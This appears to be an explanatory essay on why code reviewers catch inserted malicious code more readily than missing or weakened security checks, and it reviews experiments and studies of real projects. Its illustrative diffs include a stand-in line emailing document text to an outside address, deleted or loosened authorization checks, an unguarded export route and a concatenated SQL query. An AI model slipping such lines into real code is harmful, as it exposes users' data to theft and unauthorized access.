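# Finding missing and weakened security checks in code review, compared with finding inserted malicious code

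## What a reviewer sees when a check is added, removed, weakened or never written

In code review, someone other than the author reads a change to a program before it takes effect. Programmers use it to catch bugs, keep code readable and, in many organisations, keep out security flaws. A change can harm security by adding something hostile, such as code that sends customer records to a stranger. It can also leave the program without a check it needs, in which case the program still works but serves people it should turn away. Reviewers seem to notice hostile additions more readily than missing checks, although some of the evidence is indirect and some of it conflicts.

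The 2017 edition of the *Code Review Guide* from OWASP, a web-security foundation, defines security review as verifying that the proper controls are present, work as intended and are invoked in the right places. To do this, the reviewer has to know which controls the program needs, and the change under review may not indicate them.

### Pull requests and diffs

Most teams keep their code in a repository, a collection of files with a full history of edits. To change the code, a programmer edits a separate copy (a branch) and then opens a pull request, a proposed change that others review before anyone merges it into the project. GitHub, a widely used code host, describes the parts of a pull request in its documentation page *About pull requests*. One tab holds the author's description and the discussion, another holds the results of automated tests, and the "Files changed" tab holds the diff,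 on which reviewers comment line by line.

A diff shows a change as added and deleted lines with a little surrounding code. A plus sign marks an added line and a minus sign marks a deleted one. An altered line appears twice, the old version with a minus and the new version with a plus. Lines with no sign are unchanged context, typically three above and three below each edit. The rest of the repository is not shown unless the reviewer chooses to open it. According to GitHub's *Pull requests*, reviewers use the diff to understand a proposed change, but a diff cannot show a line that nobody wrote.

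### Validation, authorization and escaping

A security check is code that refuses or cleans something unsafe. It is often a single line. Input validation tests that data from outside has an acceptable form and range before the program uses it:

```python
if not 1 <= copies <= 10: abort(400)
```

A request to print 5,000 copies now returns an error. MDN's *Input validation*, part of a reference work for web developers, separates syntactic validation (whether the input is a number) from semantic validation (whether the number is within bounds). It also warns against relying on checks in the browser, because an attacker can skip the web page and send a request straight to the server.

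Authorization decides whether this user may perform this action on this object:

```python
if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id: abort(403)
```

Authentication, which is separate from authorization, establishes who the user is, usually with a password. People easily confuse the two, and OWASP's *Authorization Cheat Sheet* opens by distinguishing them. Logging in often doesn't entitle a user to everything the system could provide, and a visitor may be allowed to see a public page without logging in.

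Escaping rewrites data so that a database, browser or shell treats it as text and not as commands:

```python
title = html.escape(doc.title)
```

If someone has typed code into a document's title, the browser will now display the code instead of running it. Validation is no substitute for this. MDN's guidance describes generic validation as a useful but incomplete first line of defence against such attacks, because they are very hard to block without knowing where the text will end up.

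### One route and four changes

Take an invented web application in which teams store documents. A route is an address at which the server answers requests, together with the code that answers. This route returns a document only to members of the team that owns it:

```python
@app.get("/documents/<int:doc_id>")
def show_document(doc_id):
    doc = Document.get(doc_id)
    if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
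        abort(403)
    return page(doc)
```

The request supplies the document's number. The code fetches that document, compares its team with the user's team, and returns error 403 ("forbidden") if they differ. A visitor who has not logged in has no team, so the same check rejects them too.

Suppose a pull request adds one line to it:

```diff
     if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
         abort(403)
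+    mail.send("drop@outsider.example", doc.text)
     return page(doc)
```

A reviewer sees a new line that emails the text of every document anyone opens to an address outside the company. This is inserted malicious code, meaning added code whose own action is hostile. The reviewer needs to know almost nothing about the application to object. The address may belong to an archiving service the company pays for, but the reviewer can tell from the line alone that they should ask. A careful attacker would disguise the line better, for instance by reading the address from a settings file, but some added code would still have to send the text.

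Another pull request deletes the team condition:

```diff
     doc = Document.get(doc_id)
-    if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
-        abort(403)
     return page(doc)
```

The change removes a check, so anyone who can reach the server can now read any document by trying numbers. The reviewer can learn the rule from the minus lines, but must search the rest of the program to find out whether something else now enforces it. OWASP advises applying permission checks across the whole application from one place, so that nobody has to remember them for each route. A programmer who follows that advice and moves the team condition to such a place will produce the same two minus lines, and the change will be an improvement.

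The condition can also stay and become looser:

```diff
-    if doc.team_id != current_user.team_id:
+    if not current_user.is_logged_in:
         abort(403)
```

This is a weakened check, one that remains but now lets through more than it should. Every user has a login, so every user can read every team's documents. The route still has a condition and a refusal, so someone who skims will see a check and move on. To object, the reviewer has to compare the two versions and know that a login is not enough. The old line is a strong hint. But if the pull request's description reads "let teams share documents", only someone who knows whether the company decided on that can judge the change. An edit to the function that looks up a user's team could also loosen this condition without touching it, and the condition might then not appear in the diff.

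The last pull request adds a feature, in a new file:

```diff
+@app.get("/documents/<int:doc_id>/export")
+def export_document(doc_id):
+    doc = Document.get(doc_id)
+    return pdf(doc)
```

Every line is an addition, and every line does what it appears to do. The feature works. It also gives any document to anyone who asks. This is a never-written check: a needed check that new code lacks from the start, so that no line of the diff shows it. The team condition sits in another file, which the diff does not display. The reviewer must already know that documents belong to teams and that the viewing route enforces this, and must also make sure that nothing placed in front of the new route does the same job. ("Missing check" is the umbrella term for never-written and removed checks.)

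These four lines would be correct in an application whose documents are all public. Duarte, Oke and colleagues (2026) make the same point in *ABSENTIA* about a similar example, a route that requires a login and then returns whichever invoice the user names. That code is wrong only because each invoice in that application belongs to one account. They conclude that saying a check is missing is a claim about the whole application, since it is true only if no other code already keeps the caller out. Injection, where outside data reaches a database as a command, is by contrast wrong in every application.

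Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, draw a similar line in a collection of insecure pull requests that they built for testing automated reviewers. They class the deletion of a guard as a "present-type" defect, because the reviewer can point to the deleted line. Failure to add a guard is "absence-type". There the reviewer has to establish that the path is open and, separately, why it ought to be closed, for instance by citing a sibling route that does apply the check. They also grade how far away the evidence lies:

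- At L0 the changed lines are enough.
- L1 requires unchanged code in the files that the change touches.
- L2a requires code in other files that a call or an import connects to the change.
- L2b requires code in other files that resembles the changed code only in purpose.

The mailing line is an L0 case, and so is the deletion until the reviewer wonders whether the condition has moved. The export route is L2b because its only link to the viewing route is that both serve the same documents. This kind of distance probably matters to people as well as to machines. *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* (2021) reports that reviewers in Google's Chromium OS project were more likely to miss flaws that required understanding larger stretches of code.

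### Form and intent

The terms "removed", "weakened" and "never written" describe the form of a flaw but not its cause. The programmer who wrote the export route may have forgotten the condition, or may never have learned that documents have owners. MITRE's *CWE-862*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives some ordinary causes. One is converting a single-user program, which had no other users to keep out, into a multi-user one. Another is a developer's belief that attackers cannot alter certain inputs, such as cookies.

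Many of the changes that reviewers read are now written by coding agents, which are language models that read a repository, edit files and submit changes with little supervision. An agent may have left out the check because it took a shortcut and stopped once the export worked. An instruction planted in a repository file for an agent to read can lead to the same omission, and the diff looks the same in every case.

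Chen and colleagues hold that reviewers cannot infer intent, so they should treat everything the change's author controls as untrusted. If a comment above the export route reads "access already checked upstream", the reviewer should look upstream for the check. Tests in the same pull request deserve equal suspicion because they may rest on the same false assumption. This approach lets the reviewer object to the export route without accusing anyone, and the fix is the team condition whatever the motive. Motive matters later, when the team decides how far to trust the author's other changes.

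Research papers do not always distinguish the form of a change from the intent behind it. Chen and colleagues call all 89 of their insecure pull requests "malicious", yet they made 37 of them by taking a real security fix and undoing one protection in it. They use the word for the effect of merging the change, and many of the cases contain no hostile code.

### Missing authorization and access by another user's identifier

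MITRE, an American non-profit research organisation, maintains the catalogue, which is called the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE). The CWE gives each kind of software flaw a number that studies and tools use as a label. CWE-862, missing authorization, covers a program that performs no authorization check when someone tries to reach a resource or carry out an action. The deleted condition and the export route are both examples of CWE-862.

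MITRE's *CWE-639* covers programs that let one user reach another user's record by changing the value that identifies it. In OWASP's example, a bank's web address contains the account number 901, and a customer who changes it to 523 may see a stranger's transactions. The loosened condition in the document example has this flaw. CISA's *Preventing Web Application Access Control Abuse* (2023), a joint warning to developers from Australian and US security agencies, calls it an insecure direct object reference (IDOR). MITRE places it under a broader class, CWE-863 (incorrect authorization), in which the program performs a check but does so incorrectly.

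MITRE's sample code for CWE-639 looks up an invoice by number and protects the database query against injection, but it doesn't check that the invoice belongs to the user. The page lists only the user's own invoices, and the developer did not consider that someone might request a number not on the list.

CWE-862 and CWE-639 overlap. One of the examples under CWE-862 is a bulletin board that logs users in and then shows them any private message they request by number, which would fit equally well under CWE-639. Counts for either class alone therefore depend partly on which label was chosen. Of the 30 publicly disclosed access-control flaws that Duarte and colleagues collected, 15 had CWE-639 as their first label and 10 had CWE-862.

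### Odds ratio, recall, precision and F1

Experiments that compare groups of reviewers often report an odds ratio. Suppose that 100 people review the mailing line and 80 object, while 100 others review the export route and 40 object (the figures are invented). The detection rates are 80% and 40%, so the first is twice the second. The odds are the number who objected divided by the number who did not, which is 80/20 = 4 for the mailing line and 40/60 ≈ 0.67 for the export route. The odds ratio is one group's odds divided by the other's, here 6. Readers can easily misread this as "six times as many reviewers objected". The odds ratio is close to the ratio of detection rates only when detection is rare. If 8 and 4 out of 100 had objected, the first rate would still be twice the second, but the odds ratio would be about 2.1.

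Recall and precision suit anything that produces a list of suspected flaws, for example a static analysis tool, which examines source code without running it. Say that a set of changes contains ten missing checks and a tool makes twelve reports, of which six are right. Recall is the share of real flaws that the tool reported, 6/10 or 60%. Precision is the share of reports that are real flaws, 6/12 or 50%. F1 combines them in one number:

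F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

F1 is about 55% here. The formula keeps F1 close to the lower of precision and recall. For example, if an application had 200 routes and ten were unguarded, a tool that flagged all 200 would have a recall of 100% and a precision of 5%. The plain average would be 52.5%, but F1 would be just under 10%.

Measuring recall also requires knowing how many flaws exist, which nobody knows for a working project. Researchers can seed omissions by deliberately leaving checks out of a test change to measure whether review or tests catch them, or they can count only flaws that are already known. Duarte and colleagues took the second approach, and their tool found 19 of the 30 disclosed flaws. That recall of 63% doesn't measure how well the tool finds undisclosed flaws in the same applications. Their precision of 51% also depends on the judgments of a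 second language model, which read the code and confirmed or rejected the reports.

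## What controlled experiments show about human reviewers

Experimenters can measure what reviewers notice by planting a flaw in a change, giving that change to many people and counting how many report the flaw. To test directly whether hostile additions are easier to notice than missing checks, they would give each reviewer some changes with hostile additions, like the mailing line, some with missing checks, like the export route, and some harmless changes. A short search found no such experiment, though one may exist. Hostile additions are attracting attention. For example, *How well can developers detect sabotage from an AI coding agent?*, an issue of the engineering leadership newsletter RDEL, discusses whether people who approve an agent's changes would notice sabotage in them.

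None of the experiments below measured how often people notice inserted malicious code, so any figure for how much easier it is to spot than a missing or weakened check would be a guess. One experiment compares two missing checks with each other, and a series of programming contests provides records of which flaws rival teams exploited.

### Two flaws in one Java change

In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) asked 146 people to review a change to a Java program that manages employees' holidays. They recruited through programmers' forums, social media and their own contacts, and gave five dollars to charity for each completed review. Of these participants, 105 had at least three years of professional programming experience, and 64% said they reviewed code daily. The researchers told participants only that the study was about code review,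 because mentioning security would have led them to look for security problems.

Random assignment gave 80 participants a version open to injection into a database, known as SQL injection. The other 66 received a version that used a number from outside without testing its range. These invented lines, in Python to match the earlier examples, have the same two flaws:

```python
query = "SELECT * FROM employees WHERE id = '" + employee_id + "'"
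```

```python
employee.days_left -= days_requested
```

The first line inserts whatever the user typed into a database command, so a user who includes a quotation mark can alter the command. The other line subtracts the requested days from the employee's allowance, so someone who requests minus ten days gains ten. Adding a line that rejects any number below 1 would fix this second problem.

The two versions were 137 and 145 lines long. Reviewers could find either flaw, and work out how to exploit it, from the changed code alone. Both are L0 cases, the easiest kind, on Chen and colleagues' scale of how far away the evidence is.

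The researchers also planted an ordinary bug, a mishandled corner case, in both versions to check reviewers' effort. If the people who missed the security flaw had mostly missed this bug too, they might have just skimmed the code. The group with the unchecked quantity did slightly better on the bug than the other group, but chance could easily explain the difference (p = 0.38). Lack of effort therefore can't account for the results on the security flaws.

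| | SQL injection | Unchecked quantity |
|---|---|---|
| Reviewers | 80 | 66 |
| Found the ordinary bug | 39 (49%) | 37 (56%) |
| Found the security flaw in the first review | 52 (65%) | 14 (21%) |
| Found it only after a warning | 13 of the other 28 (46%) | 7 of the other 52 (13%) |
| Never found it | 15 (19%) | 45 (68%) |

In the first review, 52 of 80 reviewers (65%) found the injection and 14 of 66 (21%) found the unchecked quantity, so the detection rate was about three times as high for the injection. With groups of this size, the true ratio of rates could plausibly lie between about 2 and 5. The paper reports an odds ratio of 6.9 (95% confidence interval 3.3 to 14.6), which is the odds of finding the injection (52/28, or about 1.86) divided by the odds of finding the unchecked quantity (14/52, or about 0.27). It describes developers as "seven times more likely" to detect the injection,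 which is the usual misreading of an odds ratio as a ratio of rates.

The paper's text gives 18% for the quantity group, but its table gives 14 of 66, or 21%. The table is probably right, because the paper also reports that 66 participants found their flaw in the first review, and 52 plus 14 is 66.

Braz and colleagues then fitted a regression, a model that estimates the effect of each factor while holding the others constant. The type of flaw still had the clearest effect, with a coefficient of 2.35, or an odds ratio of about 10. People who had reviewed code more often in the past year did better, as did those who said they think about vulnerabilities while writing code. Security courses and years of professional experience had no detectable effect, but with some twenty factors and only 146 people, the regression could easily have missed a moderate one.

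### What a warning added

After the first review, the researchers told participants that the study was about security, explained what a vulnerability is, and asked about their training and habits. They then told everyone that the change they had just reviewed contained a vulnerability, without naming its type, and invited those who had not found it to look again.

Nearly half of the people who had missed the injection now found it. Of those who had missed the unchecked quantity, about one in eight did. Over both reviews, 65 of 80 people (81%) found the injection and 21 of 66 (32%) found the quantity flaw. (The text and tables disagree here too. The text gives 40% for the quantity flaw overall, and says that 91% of those who never found their flaw had the quantity version. By the tables it was 45 of 60, or 75%.)

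Inattention to security explains part of the initial failure. In 13 comments, participants in the injection group who succeeded on the second attempt said they had needed a reminder about security. One participant wrote of "looking mainly for good programming practices" the first time. But inattention explains much less of the failure with the quantity flaw. Two-thirds of that group did not find the vulnerability even when they knew the 145-line change contained one. In eight comments, participants in this group mistook the ordinary bug for the vulnerability. When a warning doesn't name the type of flaw, some reviewers apparently stop at the first defect they find.

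The warning may not explain all of the gain. No comparison group reviewed the code again without a warning, so some people may have succeeded just because they read the code twice, or because the questions about security had already made them think about it. Three comments came from people who had noticed the injection the first time but were not sure enough to mention it until they were warned. A 2022 experiment went further and tested specific instructions and checklists.

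### A familiar pattern and an unfamiliar one

Both flaws in the experiment are checks that were never written, so the results don't show that reviewers catch additions and miss omissions. Braz and colleagues class both as improper input validation, although the usual fix for injection is closer to escaping. Nobody in the experiment saw a removed check, a weakened check or malicious code.

The difference was whether the code showed a well-known route of attack. A query built by joining pieces of text is the textbook example of SQL injection. Reviewers who found it most often said that it is common and easy to notice (18 mentions) or that they had seen it before (13 mentions). An experienced reviewer can recognise this flaw from how the code looks, without thinking about what the program should refuse. In that sense the experiment is encouraging about omissions, since 65% of reviewers noticed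 a missing protection when a suspicious line revealed it.

The unchecked subtraction looks like any other subtraction, so reviewers had to think about what would happen if the number were negative without a visible cue to do so. Those who caught it mostly credited a routine, such as checking every value that a user supplies (10 mentions).

So the experiment supports the claim that reviewers catch visible, familiar patterns. SQL injection is both visible and familiar, while finding the quantity flaw also takes a little reasoning, because a reviewer has to see that subtracting a negative number of holidays gives the employee more of them. With one example of each kind, the experiment cannot separate the effects of visibility, familiarity and reasoning. Reviewers might also have missed an obscure but visible flaw, and they might have caught a well-known omission more than 21% of the time, even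 with no suspicious line to notice.

Applying these results to the document application requires some extrapolation. The mailing line resembles the glued query because the problem is visible in the code, and sending data to an outside address is a familiar warning sign. The export route is closer to the subtraction because each of its lines looks ordinary. It is probably even harder to spot, since the missing team condition is in another file, whereas the participants had everything they needed in view. The deleted condition is hard to compare with either because, although the minus lines are visible, the experiment did not test whether people recognise a deletion as readily as a glued query.

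The setting could also have biased the results in either direction. Participants reviewed a stranger's code for a program they would never run, with no colleagues to ask and nothing at stake. Braz and colleagues accept that people may be more attentive in their own projects, and a maintainer would also know things about the holiday rules that a volunteer could not. But the change was short and self-contained, unlike many real changes, which may have made the review easier.

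### Contests in which teams attack each other's programs

In the University of Maryland's Build It, Break It, Fix It contests, teams have just under two weeks to write a program to a common specification. They then act as attackers, searching their rivals' source code for vulnerabilities, and later repair their own programs. Searching a rival's code is a kind of security review, although the teams read a whole program instead of a diff and can also run it.

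Votipka, Fulton and colleagues (2020), in *Understanding security mistakes developers make*, analysed 94 programs from four of these contests. About three-quarters of the teams were taking the contest as the final part of an online series of security courses, and participants had programmed for nearly nine years on average. Teams had to build a tamper-resistant log, a cash machine that communicates with its bank, or a database in which each owner decides who may read and change the data.

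The researchers identified 182 distinct flaws and sorted them by cause. In 72 cases the team had not attempted a necessary protection, which the paper calls "no implementation". Another 71 were misunderstandings, where a team attempted the protection but got the idea wrong, for example by encrypting data with a fixed value where the method needs a random one. The remaining 39 were mistakes by programmers who had the right idea.

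"No implementation" is broader than "never-written check". It includes, for instance, logs without encryption, but also some omissions similar to the missing check on the export route. The database needed nine access-control checks, and 10 of the 15 teams that built one left out at least one check. Several did not check authorization on administrator-only commands. No team left out all nine. Their programs had checks in most places but lacked one somewhere, as the document application does after the export feature is added.

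Rival teams exploited 38 of the 39 mistakes (97%), but only 71% of the misunderstandings and absent protections combined. They exploited each of these two categories significantly less often than mistakes. At first sight, this strongly supports the idea that people overlook what is missing.

The researchers, however, rated 42 of the 72 absent protections easy to find, meaning that an attacker could discover them just by watching the program's inputs and outputs. They rated misunderstandings hard to find significantly more often than absent protections. If absent protections were easy to notice and teams still failed to exploit many of them, the difficulty must often have been in turning the discovery into a working attack.

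This matters because a team scored only if it submitted a test case that demonstrated the flaw. One team encrypted its log but left out a message authentication code, a value that reveals tampering. Anyone who read the source could see the omission, but no rival exploited it, probably because the altered file still had to decrypt into correctly structured data, and finding a suitable alteration could have taken a great many attempts. *Build It, Break It, Fix It Contests* (2020), a shorter account by the same researchers, uses this case to distinguish how easy a flaw is to find from how easy it is to exploit. The researchers rated 22 of 49 omissions hard to exploit when the need for the protection was not obvious from the specification, and none when it was obvious. The gap between 97% and 71% is therefore weaker evidence of a difference in noticing flaws than it seems.

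Missing protections were probably easier to find here than they would be in a pull request. Every team worked from the same specification and had just written its own version of the program, so it could look for omissions by checking the rival's code against each requirement. Votipka and colleagues note that, for the banking problem, an auditor could simply look for encryption, an integrity check and protection against replayed messages. The reviewer of the export route has no such list unless someone has written down that documents belong to teams. Each program also had far more readers than an ordinary change gets, with an average of 27 teams per contest plus two of the researchers. A flaw counted as exploited if any one team succeeded, so 71% is not the chance that a single reviewer would find an omission.

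### Finding missing checks by accident

A later study, *Understanding the How and the Why* (Fulton, Votipka and colleagues, 2022), gives more detail on how teams found the flaws. The researchers ran the contest as a three-week university course in which 14 student teams built a smart-home controller. Its users could grant each other permission to read or change particular devices and data. At the end of the building week, 79 flaws remained.

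| Flaw remaining after the building week | Exploited by another team | Not exploited |
|---|---|---|
| Protection never implemented | 20 | 9 |
| – some access-control checks missing | 3 | 4 |
| – no check on the chain of granted permissions | 14 | 5 |
| – no timeout | 3 | 0 |
| Misunderstanding | 17 | 8 |
| Mistake | 22 | 3 |

The proportions exploited were 69% for protections never implemented, 68% for misunderstandings and 88% for mistakes. These groups are small enough that the difference could be due to chance, but the order agrees with the larger study. Among the omissions, missing access-control checks, the flaw most like the one in the export route, were exploited least often. Three of the seven were exploited, but seven cases are too few to support a rate.

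The students had to explain each attack in writing, and their explanations show that teams mostly found missing access-control checks while testing something related. One team discovered that a rival's program did not check permissions on a particular command while testing what happens when users grant permissions to each other in a circle. Fulton and colleagues suggest that four gaps went unexploited because nobody happened to trigger them. Teams also preferred to attack obvious problems, such as programs that could not handle their input, and left subtler ones alone.

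By contrast, attackers exploited all three missing timeouts. The specification gave them a definite requirement to test, that the controller must give up on a silent script after 30 seconds, so they sent malformed scripts and watched whether the program hung.

Students also found mistakes by accident, and they found nearly all of them. The difference may be in how easily testers notice each kind of flaw. Many of the mistakes made the program crash or hang on odd input, which a tester will notice whatever they were testing. A missing authorization check shows up only when someone tries the command as a user who should be refused, so a tester who always logs in as the owner will never notice it.

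To measure noticing separately from exploiting, the course let teams submit a written report that pointed to the insecure lines and explained why a demonstration was not feasible. No team did, so these figures are again counts of successful attacks. The attackers were students, whom Fulton and colleagues expect to be weaker at finding vulnerabilities than professionals.

The records from the building week show some of what authors notice in their own code. During the week, 22 flaws were a complete lack of access control, and the teams fixed all of them. In another 10 cases only some checks were missing, and the teams fixed three. The comparison overstates how well the teams noticed missing access control, because several had deliberately written the working features first and planned to add protection later. The remaining gaps belonged to three teams that wrote basic commands in the last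 three days and forgot the checks. All three had put a separate check inside each command instead of calling one shared function, so they had to remember to add a check to every new command. OWASP's advice to apply permission checks from one place is meant to prevent this.

### Experience and false alarms

There is only thin evidence that giving security-sensitive changes to more experienced people helps. Votipka and colleagues found no link between the flaws that teams introduced and their years of programming or security training. That finding concerns writing code, but they also cite an earlier experiment in which 30 hired developers reviewed a small web application with seven known flaws. None found all seven, and more experienced reviewers were not necessarily more accurate. Braz and colleagues did find an advantage for people who review often, though such people have not necessarily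 worked for many years.

In the web-application experiment, developers who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones. They may have succeeded partly because they were more willing to raise doubts, but this makes more work for the code's author, who has to answer each one. The Java experiment could not measure this extra work because every participant received a change that contained a vulnerability.

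## What reviews of real projects caught and missed

Large open-source projects publish their old code reviews, including the comments and each version of the change. Researchers can search these records for flaws that reviewers pointed out. They can also start from a vulnerability discovered later, work out which change introduced it, and find the review that approved that change. Comparing the flaws reviewers caught with the ones they missed gives some idea of what reviewers notice in their own projects, where they know the code and have a stake in it.

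The studies sort flaws by type, such as "buffer overflow" or "improper access control". They do not record whether a check was removed, weakened or never written, so a reader has to guess this from the type, which indicates it only roughly.

### Chromium

Reviewers of Chromium, the open-source browser on which Google builds Chrome, seldom mention security. For *A security perspective on code review*, di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli (2016) read 1,155 randomly chosen review comments from 2014 and found only 11 that raised a security problem.

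Eleven cases were too few to analyse, so the researchers searched for comments containing words such as "overflow" and "sanitize". They kept 71 in which a reviewer had raised a real problem and the author had then fixed it. For the other group, they took vulnerabilities published in 2015 and traced 114 of them back to the reviews that had let them in. (The paper's abstract swaps the two figures, but its text and tables agree on 71 found and 114 missed.)

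Reviewers found 71 flaws and missed 114. They found 15 cases of cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's code runs in a page that someone else is viewing, and missed 12. They found 6 buffer overruns, where a program writes past the end of the memory set aside for some data, and missed 18. For a group of C++ errors that includes using memory after releasing it, they found 8 and missed 33. They missed all 7 cases of command injection.

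Several of these types often come down to a missing check. Cross-site scripting and command injection usually happen because the code doesn't escape some outside data, and a buffer overrun can happen because the code copies data without first checking its size. Reviewers therefore did comparatively well on one kind of missing check and badly on others. Di Biase and colleagues suggest that people who work on a browser are alert to browser-specific dangers and less alert to those that any program might have.

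Reviewers missed a surprising number of memory errors, even though a reader can often confirm one from the changed lines and a little nearby code.

### Chromium OS

Paul, Turzo and Bosu made a larger comparison in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, using the reviews of Chromium OS, Google's operating system built around the browser. From 404,878 reviews between 2011 and 2019 they identified 516 in which a reviewer had found a security flaw. They then took 239 flaws from the project's bug tracker and traced them to 374 reviews that had approved the faulty code. These are the main types:

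| Type of flaw | Reviews that found it | Reviews that missed it |
|---|---|---|
| Use of a dangerous function | 53 | 0 |
| Resource not properly released | 71 | 4 |
| Synchronisation errors, including race conditions | 182 | 23 |
| Incorrect calculation | 65 | 17 |
| Unusual conditions not checked or handled | 58 | 22 |
| Access outside a memory buffer | 42 | 16 |
| Exposing a resource to the wrong users or programs | 15 | 35 |
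| Improper access control | 8 | 58 |
| Improper input validation | 9 | 72 |
| Use of a resource after its release | 3 | 62 |
| Insufficient verification that data is authentic | 0 | 13 |

Input validation and access control are the two flaw types closest to the missing checks in the document application. Together they make up 17 of the 512 found flaws in the paper's full table (3%) and 130 of the 353 missed flaws (37%). Dangerous functions show the opposite pattern. These are C functions such as `strcpy`, which copies text without checking that it fits, and a reviewer can recognise them by name.

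But other omissions were among the flaws that reviewers found most often. Failing to release a resource is an omission, and failing to handle an error often is too. Reviewers may catch these because a line in the diff prompts them to look for the missing code. Code that opens a file should close it, and code that calls a function should handle the function's failure. The export route contains no such prompt. Paul and colleagues give a similar explanation, based on how much surrounding code a reviewer has to understand, and add that some validation flaws show up only when someone runs the program.

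How the researchers collected the cases probably exaggerates the contrast. They found successful reviews by searching the comments for 105 keywords, which include "race", "leak", "overflow" and the names of several dangerous functions, but not "validate" or "authorization". The study would not have counted a reviewer who caught a missing check by asking "who is allowed to call this?" The missed cases came from bugs that the project had labelled as security problems. If reviewers overlooked a dangerous function that later caused a problem, the bug might well be recorded as a buffer overflow, which would help to explain the zero in the first row.

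Checks that were never written are also hard to trace to their origin. Researchers normally trace a flaw by finding the lines that the repair altered and using the version history to see who last changed them. If the repair only adds a check, there is no faulty line to look up. Paul and colleagues instead looked up the lines just before and after the addition, reasoning that security repairs often insert a check right before an access or after a function call, and inspected the results by hand. But the neighbouring lines may have been written years before the check became necessary.

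### Directories, experience and familiarity

Paul and colleagues also fitted a regression to find which factors were associated with reviewers finding the flaw. The number of directories that a change touched had the most explanatory power. The odds ratio was 0.76 for each additional directory, so a review with a 50% chance of finding the flaw would have about a 43% chance if the change touched one more. The researchers left the number of files and the number of changed lines out of the model because both were correlated with the number of directories. It is therefore unclear from this result whether reviewers struggle with scattered changes, changes to many files or long changes. The distinction matters for coding agents because they can produce large changes quickly.

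Contrary to what the researchers expected, reviewers who had done more reviews were less likely to find the flaw. The odds ratio was 0.99 per earlier review, and some reviewers had done hundreds. Taken literally, this ratio means that a hundred extra reviews would cut the odds of finding the flaw by almost two-thirds, although the rounding of 0.99 alone allows for a cut of anywhere from 40% to nearly 80%. In the Java experiment by Braz and colleagues, however, frequent reviewers did better.

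Paul and colleagues suggest that people who review a great deal may tire of it or have less time for each change, or that finding security flaws may take a skill that ordinary reviewing does not build. Projects may also send their hardest changes to their most experienced people. The model included some measures of difficulty, but these could not capture everything that makes a change hard to judge.

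Familiarity with the code seemed to help. Reviewers who had done a larger share of a file's earlier reviews were more likely to find the flaw (odds ratio 1.83), as were those who had often exchanged reviews with the author. The regression combines all types of flaw, so it can't show whether familiarity helps with missing checks specifically. That would make sense, though, because someone who knows a file is more likely to know what its code should reject.

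Reviewers were also more likely to find flaws in changes that fixed bugs, with an odds ratio of 4.55. Adding reviewers made no detectable difference. Di Biase and colleagues had recommended more than two reviewers because 39 of their 71 successful reviews had that many, but they did not count reviewers in the unsuccessful ones.

### OpenSSL, PHP, OpenStack and Qt

Keyword searches find only comments that contain the expected words. In *Toward Effective Secure Code Reviews* (2023), Charoenwet, Thongtanunam and colleagues instead ranked 135,560 review comments from the encryption library OpenSSL and the programming language PHP by how closely their wording resembled descriptions of 40 categories of weakness. They read 6,146 of the comments and found 311 separate security concerns.

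Authentication errors were the most common category, with 30 concerns. Five concerns, all in PHP, fell under the category that includes missing escaping, only one fell under data validation, and none fell under authorization.

The lack of comments about missing authorization doesn't show that reviewers never noticed it. OpenSSL and PHP are components that other people use to build applications, and it is mostly those applications that decide which user may open which document, so reviewers of the components had fewer authorization checks to examine. The search also missed relevant comments. To test it, the researchers read 400 of the comments in each project that the ranking had placed too low to be included, and found five that raised relevant concerns. They considered this insignificant, but scaled up to all the unread comments, it comes to roughly 700, about twice the 330 relevant comments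 they found. An estimate based on five comments could be far out, but a category with no entries may well have had some among the unread comments.

Charoenwet and colleagues then compared the concerns with the two projects' published vulnerabilities. Memory buffer errors made up 21% of the vulnerabilities in OpenSSL and 29% in PHP, but under 4% of the concerns in each. One of their examples is Heartbleed, an OpenSSL vulnerability made public in 2014. A client could send the server a short message, claim that it was longer, and receive a reply padded with other data from the server's memory. The code did not check the claimed length, and the fix added that check.

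Projects did not always fix the problems that reviewers noticed. Of 309 concerns whose outcome the researchers could trace, authors fixed 115 in the same pull request. In 23 cases, people could not agree on a solution and the project merged the change with no sign that anyone had dealt with the concern.

In *Security Defect Detection via Code Review*, Yu, Fu and colleagues (2023) examined what happened after reviewers raised security problems in four projects, two from OpenStack (software for running cloud services) and two from Qt (a toolkit for building applications). They searched 432,585 comments by keyword, read the results by hand, and found 614 about security, 539 of them written by reviewers. Of those 539, 210 concerned race conditions, 123 concerned crashes and 31 concerned improper access. The study did not collect flaws that reviewers missed, so these counts don't measure what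 went unnoticed.

Reviewers sometimes notice missing checks. A problem's solution is better evidence of its form than its type is, and authors fixed 26 of the crash problems by adding a condition that the code had lacked. Authors resolved 17 of the 31 access problems (55%), compared with 66% of problems of all types. They acted on 81% of comments that recommended a specific solution and 60% of those that only pointed out a problem. This may be because reviewers propose solutions mainly when the fix is easy, but naming the missing condition and saying where it belongs takes little effort.

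### Why the records give no detection rate

Paul and colleagues write that about 88% of the access-control flaws went undetected in review, based on 58 missed and 8 found. But a true detection rate, like recall, would also have to count the flaws that nobody has discovered, which are in neither group.

If Chromium OS had 58 more access-control flaws that nobody had discovered, reviewers would have found 8 of 124, or 6%. If reviewers had instead caught another 30 and described them without using any of the keywords, the rate would be 38 of 96, or 40%. The 58 and the 30 are hypothetical, but nothing in the records rules them out. The totals of 516 and 374 don't help determine the rate either, because they depend on how thoroughly the researchers could search each set of records. For instance, of the 591 fixed security bugs in the tracker, they could use only the 239 whose repairs had gone through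 the project's own review system.

Comparisons between types of flaw are safer than rates only if each type had a similar chance of being recorded, which is doubtful. As in the programming contests, a missing authorization check seldom attracts attention the way a crash does. Missing authorization checks have therefore probably gone undiscovered more often than memory errors, which would make reviewers' record on authorization even worse than it appears.

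### Debian's random numbers

Individual cases can show details that the studies' categories leave out, such as what the diff displayed and who looked at it. But famous cases are a biased sample, because people write about changes that did damage or nearly did, and hardly ever about a reviewer who asked for a missing condition and got it added.

Debian, a widely used version of Linux, distributes its own copy of OpenSSL. In 2006 a user complained that Valgrind, a tool that finds memory errors, gave warnings about OpenSSL's random-number generator. The generator keeps a pool of unpredictable data from which the library makes encryption keys, and the warnings led to a line that stirs new data into the pool:

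```c
MD_Update(&m,buf,j);
```

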